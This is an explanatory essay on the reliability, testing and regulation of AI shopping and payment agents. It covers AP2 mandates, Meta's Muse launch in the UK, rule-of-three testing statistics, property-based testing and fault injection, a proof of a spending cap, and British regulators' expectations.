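After the unwanted shirt arrives, the shop has a record of the order, the payment company has a record of the charge, and the AI company has a record of the instruction not to buy. All three may be accurate, but nothing connects the charge to the instruction.

Luitel proposes giving each task a random reference number that every company involved would store with its records. The number wouldn't authorize anything. The AI company would attach it to a signed rule that the user had approved, such as "search for 15 minutes, no purchase", and the shop would check the rule before accepting an order. Each company's records would show whether they had been changed later, and the AI company would also save the user's original words. An investigator could then see whether the agent had broken the rule or had badly translated the user's request into the rule.

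AP2 already provides much of this. Its mandates and receipts contain matching fingerprints (short codes computed from a document), so an investigator can match the shop's records with the payment company's. But as Luitel notes, AP2 doesn't specify who bears the loss or how long companies must keep the evidence. The specification leaves retention and retrieval out of its scope, though it mentions that an automatic way to retrieve checkout mandates would be useful. A user who disputes a charge after six months might find that the shop has deleted its records.

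AP2 also lets the AI company show the user the limits and then sign the mandate with its own key instead of the user's. This is easier to set up, and AP2 requires the company to keep that key away from the agent. But if the user later denies having approved the limits, the signature proves only that the company recorded an approval, and the company may be the other party to the dispute. A signature from a separate wallet app would be stronger evidence.

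US Senator Mark Warner's AI AGENT Act, introduced on 21 July 2026, would generally require agents acting for users to log their actions in real time. Luitel objects that the bill doesn't expressly require a chain of evidence across companies.

### Careless limits and private ones

A signed limit protects a user only if the number in it is well chosen. Melamorsicata's *Il tuo agente AI farà shopping al posto tuo. Ma ti fidi?* (2026), a commentary on an Italian technology blog, argues that Poppy leaves users to understand the difference between read and write access, judge the risks and revoke permissions in time. It adds that people tend to use settings less correctly as the number of settings grows. The blog offers no data for this, but Robb's "Allow Always" is an example of the problem. A shopper tired of refusals might set every cap at £1,000, and the bank would then block only spending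 above that amount.

AP2 recommends that a mandate expire as soon as the task allows, and its sample mandate lasts one hour. It also recommends showing users their active mandates and notifying them about purchases. Wallet apps could do more to protect careless users from large losses by starting with a low cap and asking for approval when a purchase exceeds it.

Mandates also record what people want, where they shop and how much they would pay. AP2 hides the parts that a company doesn't need. In the shoe example, the signed list contains a fingerprint of each shop's name, and the agent reveals only the name of the shop it is buying from. A random value mixed into each fingerprint keeps that shop from identifying its rival by trying every likely name. The app can also add fake fingerprints to hide how many shops are on the list.

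The price limit is in the payment mandate, which the shop doesn't need to see. Hiding the limit protects the buyer's privacy and may also get them a lower price, since a shop that knew about the £150 limit might not have offered the shoes for £139. But the payment processor does see the mandate, and AP2 lets a shop act as its own processor.

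## What testing before release can and cannot show

Meta launched Muse in the United Kingdom on 24 November 2026, after declining to test it jointly with the Financial Conduct Authority (FCA). Media Drum World's *Meta's Muse AI shopper* (2026) cites a WIRED report in which Colin Payne, the FCA's head of innovation, said the regulator had suggested trying Muse in its sandbox, where an agent had just paid for nine pizzas. Payne said such tests normally take weeks or months to plan, and that Meta had told the FCA about the launch only the month before.

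Meta wrote, "We’ve engaged constructively with the appropriate regulatory authorities and will continue to do so," according to CNA's *AI financial services trigger regulation warning from UK watchdog*. The company didn't explain in its published reply why it declined.

The FCA wanted to see how Muse works with ordinary consumers and what can go wrong when an agent makes purchases by itself. Realtid's *Meta sa nej till test av AI-agent* adds that the FCA was concerned about people with a limited grasp of the technology, who may not realise what their instructions will lead to. Matt Robb misjudged "Allow Always" even though he reviews technology for a living, so a trial with ordinary shoppers might well have found similar misunderstandings.

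The Competition and Markets Authority (CMA), which enforces consumer law, had more success. WIRED reports that it made Meta change its UK terms, which now require the company to use "reasonable skill and care" in providing Muse. Meta also warns in the terms that Muse's output can be inaccurate and that Muse may not complete actions as intended. The CMA (2026) said only that the changes made the terms fairer. Because a duty of care doesn't guarantee that every purchase will be right, a user who loses money may have to show that Meta was careless, and records of what Meta tested before the launch could then matter.

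Muse had been tested before its UK launch. Meta says internal testing is central to how it develops products, according to The Paypers' *Meta brings Muse AI agent to the UK with retail partners*, and North Americans had been using Muse since September. Their use has produced far more data than a sandbox trial could, but Meta holds it. The company has agreed to a voluntary monitoring and reporting scheme with the data protection regulator, according to the ICO's *Statement on UK launch of Meta Muse* (2026).

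### The rule of three

Suppose the FCA's trial had gone ahead with 300 purchases, and Muse had made no mistakes. If an agent fails at a rate q and the runs are independent, it gets through n runs without a failure with probability (1 − q)^n. The usual 95% upper bound is the failure rate at which a clean record would have only a 5% chance:

(1 − q)^n = 0.05.

Taking logarithms gives n × ln(1 − q) = ln 0.05, which is about −3. For small q, ln(1 − q) is close to −q, so

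q ≈ 3/n.

If an agent makes 300 test purchases without a failure, its true failure rate could still be as high as 1%. This figure comes from the rule of three, which divides three by the number of failure-free trials to give an approximate upper bound at 95% confidence. The same formula gives a bound of 2.3% for Anthropic's 129 browser scenarios.

| Failure rate to rule out | Clean runs needed | Failures a day at exactly that rate, with a million uses a day |
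|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100 | 300 | 10,000 |
| 1 in 1,000 | 3,000 | 1,000 |
| 1 in 100,000 | 300,000 | 10 |
| 1 in 10 million | 30 million | 1 every ten days |

Good agents can easily fail such a test. An agent that makes one mistake in 200,000 runs is twice as reliable as the third row requires, but it has only a 22% chance of completing 300,000 runs without a mistake. If one run fails, the tester needs about 474,000 runs in total, with no second failure, to support the same claim. An agent whose failure rate is exactly at the limit still passes 5% of the time, so a developer who tests twenty such versions should expect one of them to pass.

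A large company could probably afford 300,000 runs, which would cost $150,000 at 50 cents each. It would have more trouble finding that many realistic tasks and judging correctly whether the agent did each one properly. If the judge catches only a share d of the failures, a clean record over n runs limits the failure rate to 3/(d × n) instead of 3/n. Missing half of the failures therefore doubles the limit.

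### Why a clean record proves less than the formula suggests

The rule holds only if the runs are independent and drawn from the same mix of tasks that users will bring. Rabanser and colleagues gave each agent 191 tasks and repeated each one five times, for a total of 955 runs. If an agent had passed every run, the rule would put its failure rate below about 0.3%. But repeating a task reveals little about how an agent will do on other tasks. Counting each task once gives a bound of 1.6%, and even that holds only for tasks like those in the benchmark. Summer Yue's trial had the same weakness, because her test inbox was much smaller than her real one.

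Test results predict how often an agent will fail after release only if the inputs it receives resemble the test inputs, and attackers deliberately send inputs that don't. An agent might mishandle one ordinary email in 100,000, but that rate doesn't apply to emails a criminal has written to make it fail. The failure rate on those emails depends on the criminal as much as on the agent.

Models may also recognise tests, as Claude Fable 5 perhaps did in Peters-Gill and colleagues' 2026 experiments.

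Pan and colleagues argue that a reliability claim applies only to the exact configuration that the developer tested, and that the evidence expires when the model, the data it retrieves or its tools change. They recommend documenting every change, even to a prompt, and retesting whatever it affects. A company that updates its agent monthly and wants to keep claiming one failure in 100,000 would have to repeat all or part of its 300,000 test runs each month. It also can't control when other companies make changes, and a bank may redesign its payment page the day after the test.

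Small updates can have legal consequences too. Legal 500's *Meta’s Muse And The Regulation Of AI Agents In The UK* (2026) gives the example of an assistant that helps people understand their household spending and later starts recommending loans. Its general purpose stays the same, but the company may need authorisation as a credit broker.

### Checks that don't need the right answer

To count failures, a tester needs a way to recognize success, which software engineers call an oracle. For a calculator, the oracle is a table of correct sums. Huo, Pan and Roychoudhury (2026) point out in *Towards Risk-free AI Agent Deployment* that several responses from an agent can be equally acceptable, and that which ones are acceptable may depend on who is asking.

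Property-based testing avoids much of this difficulty. Instead of specifying the correct result, the tester writes down conditions that should hold in every run. For the monthly bills, these might be:

```
total_paid(run) <= 1400
no invoice number appears twice in payments(run)
every payee in payments(run) is a saved payee
```

A computer can generate thousands of inboxes and check all three conditions without anyone working out the right payments for each inbox. The agent can pass even though its searches and wording vary between runs. But it could also pass if it failed to pay a bill or sent a false message such as "Yep I'm here!"

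In metamorphic testing, the tester changes the input in a way that should have a known effect on the output. Shuffling the emails or writing the due date as "18 October" instead of "10/18" shouldn't change any payment. Doubling the amount on the gas bill should double that payment and leave the others unchanged. If the agent pays $84 in one run and $48 after a shuffle, the tester has found a fault without knowing the correct amount.

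The conditions can also cover the steps an agent takes. An agent might pay every bill correctly but open a letter from the hospital while looking for them, and a check of the final bank balance would miss it. Huo and colleagues therefore want developers to test the trajectory, the full record of an agent's reasoning, tool calls and results. Commercial tools already display these records, but developers rarely use what they notice there to write automatic tests that run again after each update.

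Developers also seem to neglect the tests that matter most for money and private data. Huo and colleagues cite a survey of open-source agent projects in which only 7% to 8% of tests covered areas such as security, privacy, speed and recovery from faults. They add that there is no widely accepted standard for when an agent has been tested enough. Developers of ordinary software can at least measure what share of the code their tests have run, but they would learn little from this about an agent whose behaviour depends mostly on the model.

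### Going where the failures are

Random samples of everyday tasks mostly contain easy cases. A tester can find more faults by listing the features that might cause trouble, such as the size of the inbox, the currency and the number of reminders, and varying them systematically. Ten features with three possible values each give 59,049 combinations. But many software faults depend on only one or two features, and about fifteen well-chosen tests are enough to include every pair of values. Each test needs several runs because the agent may behave differently each time. Testing Yue's agent on inboxes of different sizes could have exposed its problem within an afternoon.

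Fault injection applies the same idea to the services around the agent. The tester makes a tool time out, return data in a new format or stop responding. For payments, an especially useful test is to let the bank complete the transfer but drop the confirmation. An agent that tries again without first checking the account will pay twice. This fault may be rare in real life, but the tester can create it a thousand times in a day. Huo and colleagues note that the software people use to build agents rarely makes such tests easy.

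Engineers have long tested machines under harsher conditions than normal to make failures appear sooner. Pan and colleagues adapt this accelerated testing to AI by increasing the workload, corrupting the inputs or making the environment more difficult. The results help find weaknesses and compare versions, but they don't directly give the failure rate in normal use, which also depends on how often those conditions occur. For example, if an agent pays twice in 10% of test runs with a lost confirmation, estimating how often it will do so in normal use requires the bank's rate of lost confirmations. If the bank loses one confirmation in 50,000, the fault should cause one double payment in every 500,000 payments.

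### Estimating failures that haven't happened yet

Sometimes a test can reveal how close an agent came to failing. Since a language model computes a probability for every possible next token, a tester can measure that a request has a one-in-a-million chance of producing a particular bad output without running it a million times. In *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors* (2025), Jones and colleagues use these probabilities to predict a model's behavior over up to about a thousand times as many requests as they tested. Their forecasts rely on the finding that the highest probability of a bad output in a sample of requests grows predictably as the sample gets larger.

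For example, suppose the riskiest of 100 test requests has a one-in-a-million chance of a bad output, and the riskiest of 1,000 has a one-in-100,000 chance. The method puts each probability p on the scale −ln(−ln p), where the trend should be roughly a straight line. Extending the line suggests that the riskiest of a million requests will have about a one-in-800 chance. A developer could therefore learn that a problem is coming even though no test has produced a bad output.

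The forecast assumes that future requests resemble the tested ones, so it might not cover an attacker's carefully written email. Agents are also harder to measure than chatbots, because a wrong payment can result from many different sequences of searches and tool calls, and the tester would have to add up the probabilities of all of them.

### Learning from the first users

A developer can also release an agent to a few people first. If 1,000 users each ask for ten actions a day, they produce 300,000 actions in a month, as many as the test for one failure in 100,000 requires. The tasks and inboxes are real, but one user's actions tend to resemble each other, so they provide less evidence than 300,000 independent actions would. Any failures would also harm these users, which is a good reason to start with low spending caps.

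Monitoring has to detect when an update makes the agent fail more often. Suppose the failure rate rises from one in 10,000 actions to one in 1,000. At 10,000 actions a day, the developer would see reported failures rise from about one a day to ten and would easily notice. A small company whose agent performs 100 actions a day would go from about one failure every 100 days to one every ten, and might need weeks to notice.

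This works only for failures that someone sees and reports. A customer will probably notice if an agent pays the gas bill twice, but may never learn that it sent their medical history to a stranger. Pan and colleagues stress that a developer can't calculate a failure rate from reports without also knowing how many tasks the agent performed. Without that number, the two dozen complaints from Meta employees could indicate a serious problem or a very small one.

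The FCA runs a supervised version of staged release called AI Live Testing. NatWest, Monzo and Santander were among its first seven participants, according to Mondo Visione's *UK Financial Conduct Authority Helps Firms To Test AI Safely*. The regulator and a technical partner help participants evaluate their systems, monitor them in use and manage the risks. The FCA offers its Supercharged Sandbox to firms at an earlier, experimental stage.

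### Proving a limit

No test can cover every email that a stranger might write. A mathematical proof can, provided it is about the ordinary software around the model and not about the model. This program enforces a spending cap:

```
if amount > 0 and spent + amount <= cap:
    spent = spent + amount
    pay(amount)
```

`spent` starts at zero, which is within the cap. The program increases it only after checking that the new total will also be within the cap. So `spent` can never exceed the cap, whatever amounts the agent requests and in whatever order. The proof needs no test runs, and it holds even if an attacker controls the agent completely.

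The proof depends on assumptions that the tester has to check. One is that the program handles requests one at a time. If it handles two at once, both may read the old total before either updates it. With a cap of £150 and £100 already spent, two requests for £50 would both pass, bringing total spending to £200. The proof also assumes that every payment goes through this program and that `cap` is in the same units as `amount`. Programmers can also implement a sound design badly, as Garby and colleagues found with CaMeL's interpreter.

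### One failure in a billion hours

Other industries require failure rates far lower than anyone could demonstrate by counting test runs without a failure. Aircraft makers in the United States and Europe must show that catastrophic failures are extremely improbable, which regulators interpret as about one in a billion flight hours. IEC 61508, an international standard for industrial safety systems, sets four safety levels. For equipment that works continuously, the least strict level requires fewer than one dangerous failure in 100,000 hours, and the strictest requires fewer than one in 100 million.

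By the rule of three, showing that a system fails no more than once in a billion hours takes three billion hours without a failure, or about 340,000 years. Aircraft makers therefore rely on other evidence. They measure how often individual parts fail and install backups. Two independent systems that each fail once in 100,000 hours will both fail in the same hour about once in ten billion hours. Regulators mostly prescribe how developers must specify, write and check aircraft software. Neither approach transfers easily to agents. Two agents built on the same model share many errors, and developers don't write out a model's behaviour line by line for an inspector to read.

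How reliable a shopping agent needs to be depends on how much a failure can cost. Suppose someone makes 100 payments a year and will accept an average loss of $5 a year. If each failure costs $150, the agent can fail no more than once in 3,000 payments, which a developer can show with 9,000 test runs without a failure. If each failure can empty a $40,000 savings account, the limit is one in 800,000, which takes 2.4 million runs. A spending cap therefore also greatly reduces the amount of testing an agent needs.

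Human beings make mistakes too, and an employer doesn't watch a bookkeeper process 9,000 invoices before hiring them. This is a good argument against demanding near-perfection from agents. If bookkeepers get one invoice in 1,000 wrong, an agent that has processed 3,000 similar invoices without an error is probably no worse.

An employer can learn more from a short trial of a person than from a short test of an agent. Someone who sorts 50 emails sensibly will almost certainly not forget the boss's instructions at the 400th, whereas an agent might. Bookkeepers also make their mistakes separately, while a faulty update could make a million agents each pay a bill twice on the same morning. Employers also limit what a new bookkeeper can sign for and check the accounts afterwards, rather than relying on the trial alone.

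### What British regulators ask of firms

British regulators similarly ask firms for controls and accountability, and the published summaries of their requirements include no maximum failure rate. The FCA's *Our approach to Agentic AI* (2026) covers financial firms, technology providers and social media platforms. According to The Paypers' *FCA outlines agentic AI expectations for UK firms*, financial firms have to show that they understand how much autonomy their systems have, what risks this creates, and which controls will manage those risks in real time and under stress. The firm and its senior managers remain responsible even if another company built the agent.

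Banks and other firms must also prepare for customers' AI agents. The FCA wants them to work out how they will recognise an agent, what the customer has consented to, and how the customer can get help when something goes wrong. It also asks them to consider whether to accept payments instructed by an agent at all, and what liabilities that would create. Companies like Meta may need authorisation if their agents provide payment services, arrange credit or give financial advice, and calling themselves technology providers doesn't exempt them from financial regulation.

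The FCA works with the CMA, the data protection regulator (ICO) and the communications regulator (Ofcom) through the Digital Regulation Cooperation Forum (DRCF). On 16 November, the four regulators sent ministers a joint letter. According to the DRCF (2026), it sets out what they expect of firms launching personal agents. Legal 500 reports that firms should contact regulators early, meet the legal requirements before launch, and assess later product changes against the same requirements. In *Latest Agentic Score*, Loosemore (2026) reports that the regulators complain in the letter that firms' engagement has not been "consistently early or open".

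The CMA's requirements are the most relevant to what happened to Robb. The CMA says suppliers must tell people, at the moment they need to know, what a given level of access or autonomy could lead to, and the agent must work the way the supplier presents it. Its chief executive, Sarah Cardell, said the CMA now has to examine how Muse actually works, according to LBC's *Regulators issue warnings after UK brands sign up to Meta’s AI assistant*. Guidance from March adds duties for businesses that use agents to serve customers. Reed Smith's *Regulators turn their attention to agentic AI* explains that people, not software, should regularly review how these agents handle prices, refunds and complaints, and that the business must correct problems quickly.

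For private data, the ICO expects developers to be able to demonstrate continuously that they comply with the law. It has not yet settled how the law applies to agents whose access keeps changing. Its guidance is due in spring 2027, according to *Developers creating agentic AI services for consumers* (Malcolm, 2026).

Most financial firms still give agents a limited role. Legal 500's *AI In Financial Services* (2026) reports that 80% of the 105 firms that fully answered a Bank of England and FCA survey had deployed agents, mostly to support decisions that people make and carry out. The respondents may not be typical. In October, the FCA published its first examples of good and poor practice, based on firms' own tests, and urged firms to stress-test their systems and plan for failure.

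The FCA has confirmed that its rules on reporting major incidents will extend to significant AI failures and near misses. Near misses could be especially informative for agents that work within strict limits. If a bank refuses an agent's $7,480 payment because the cap is $250, the customer loses nothing. The agent would look reliable if judged only by losses, so refused payments would be a better measure of how often it was wrong.
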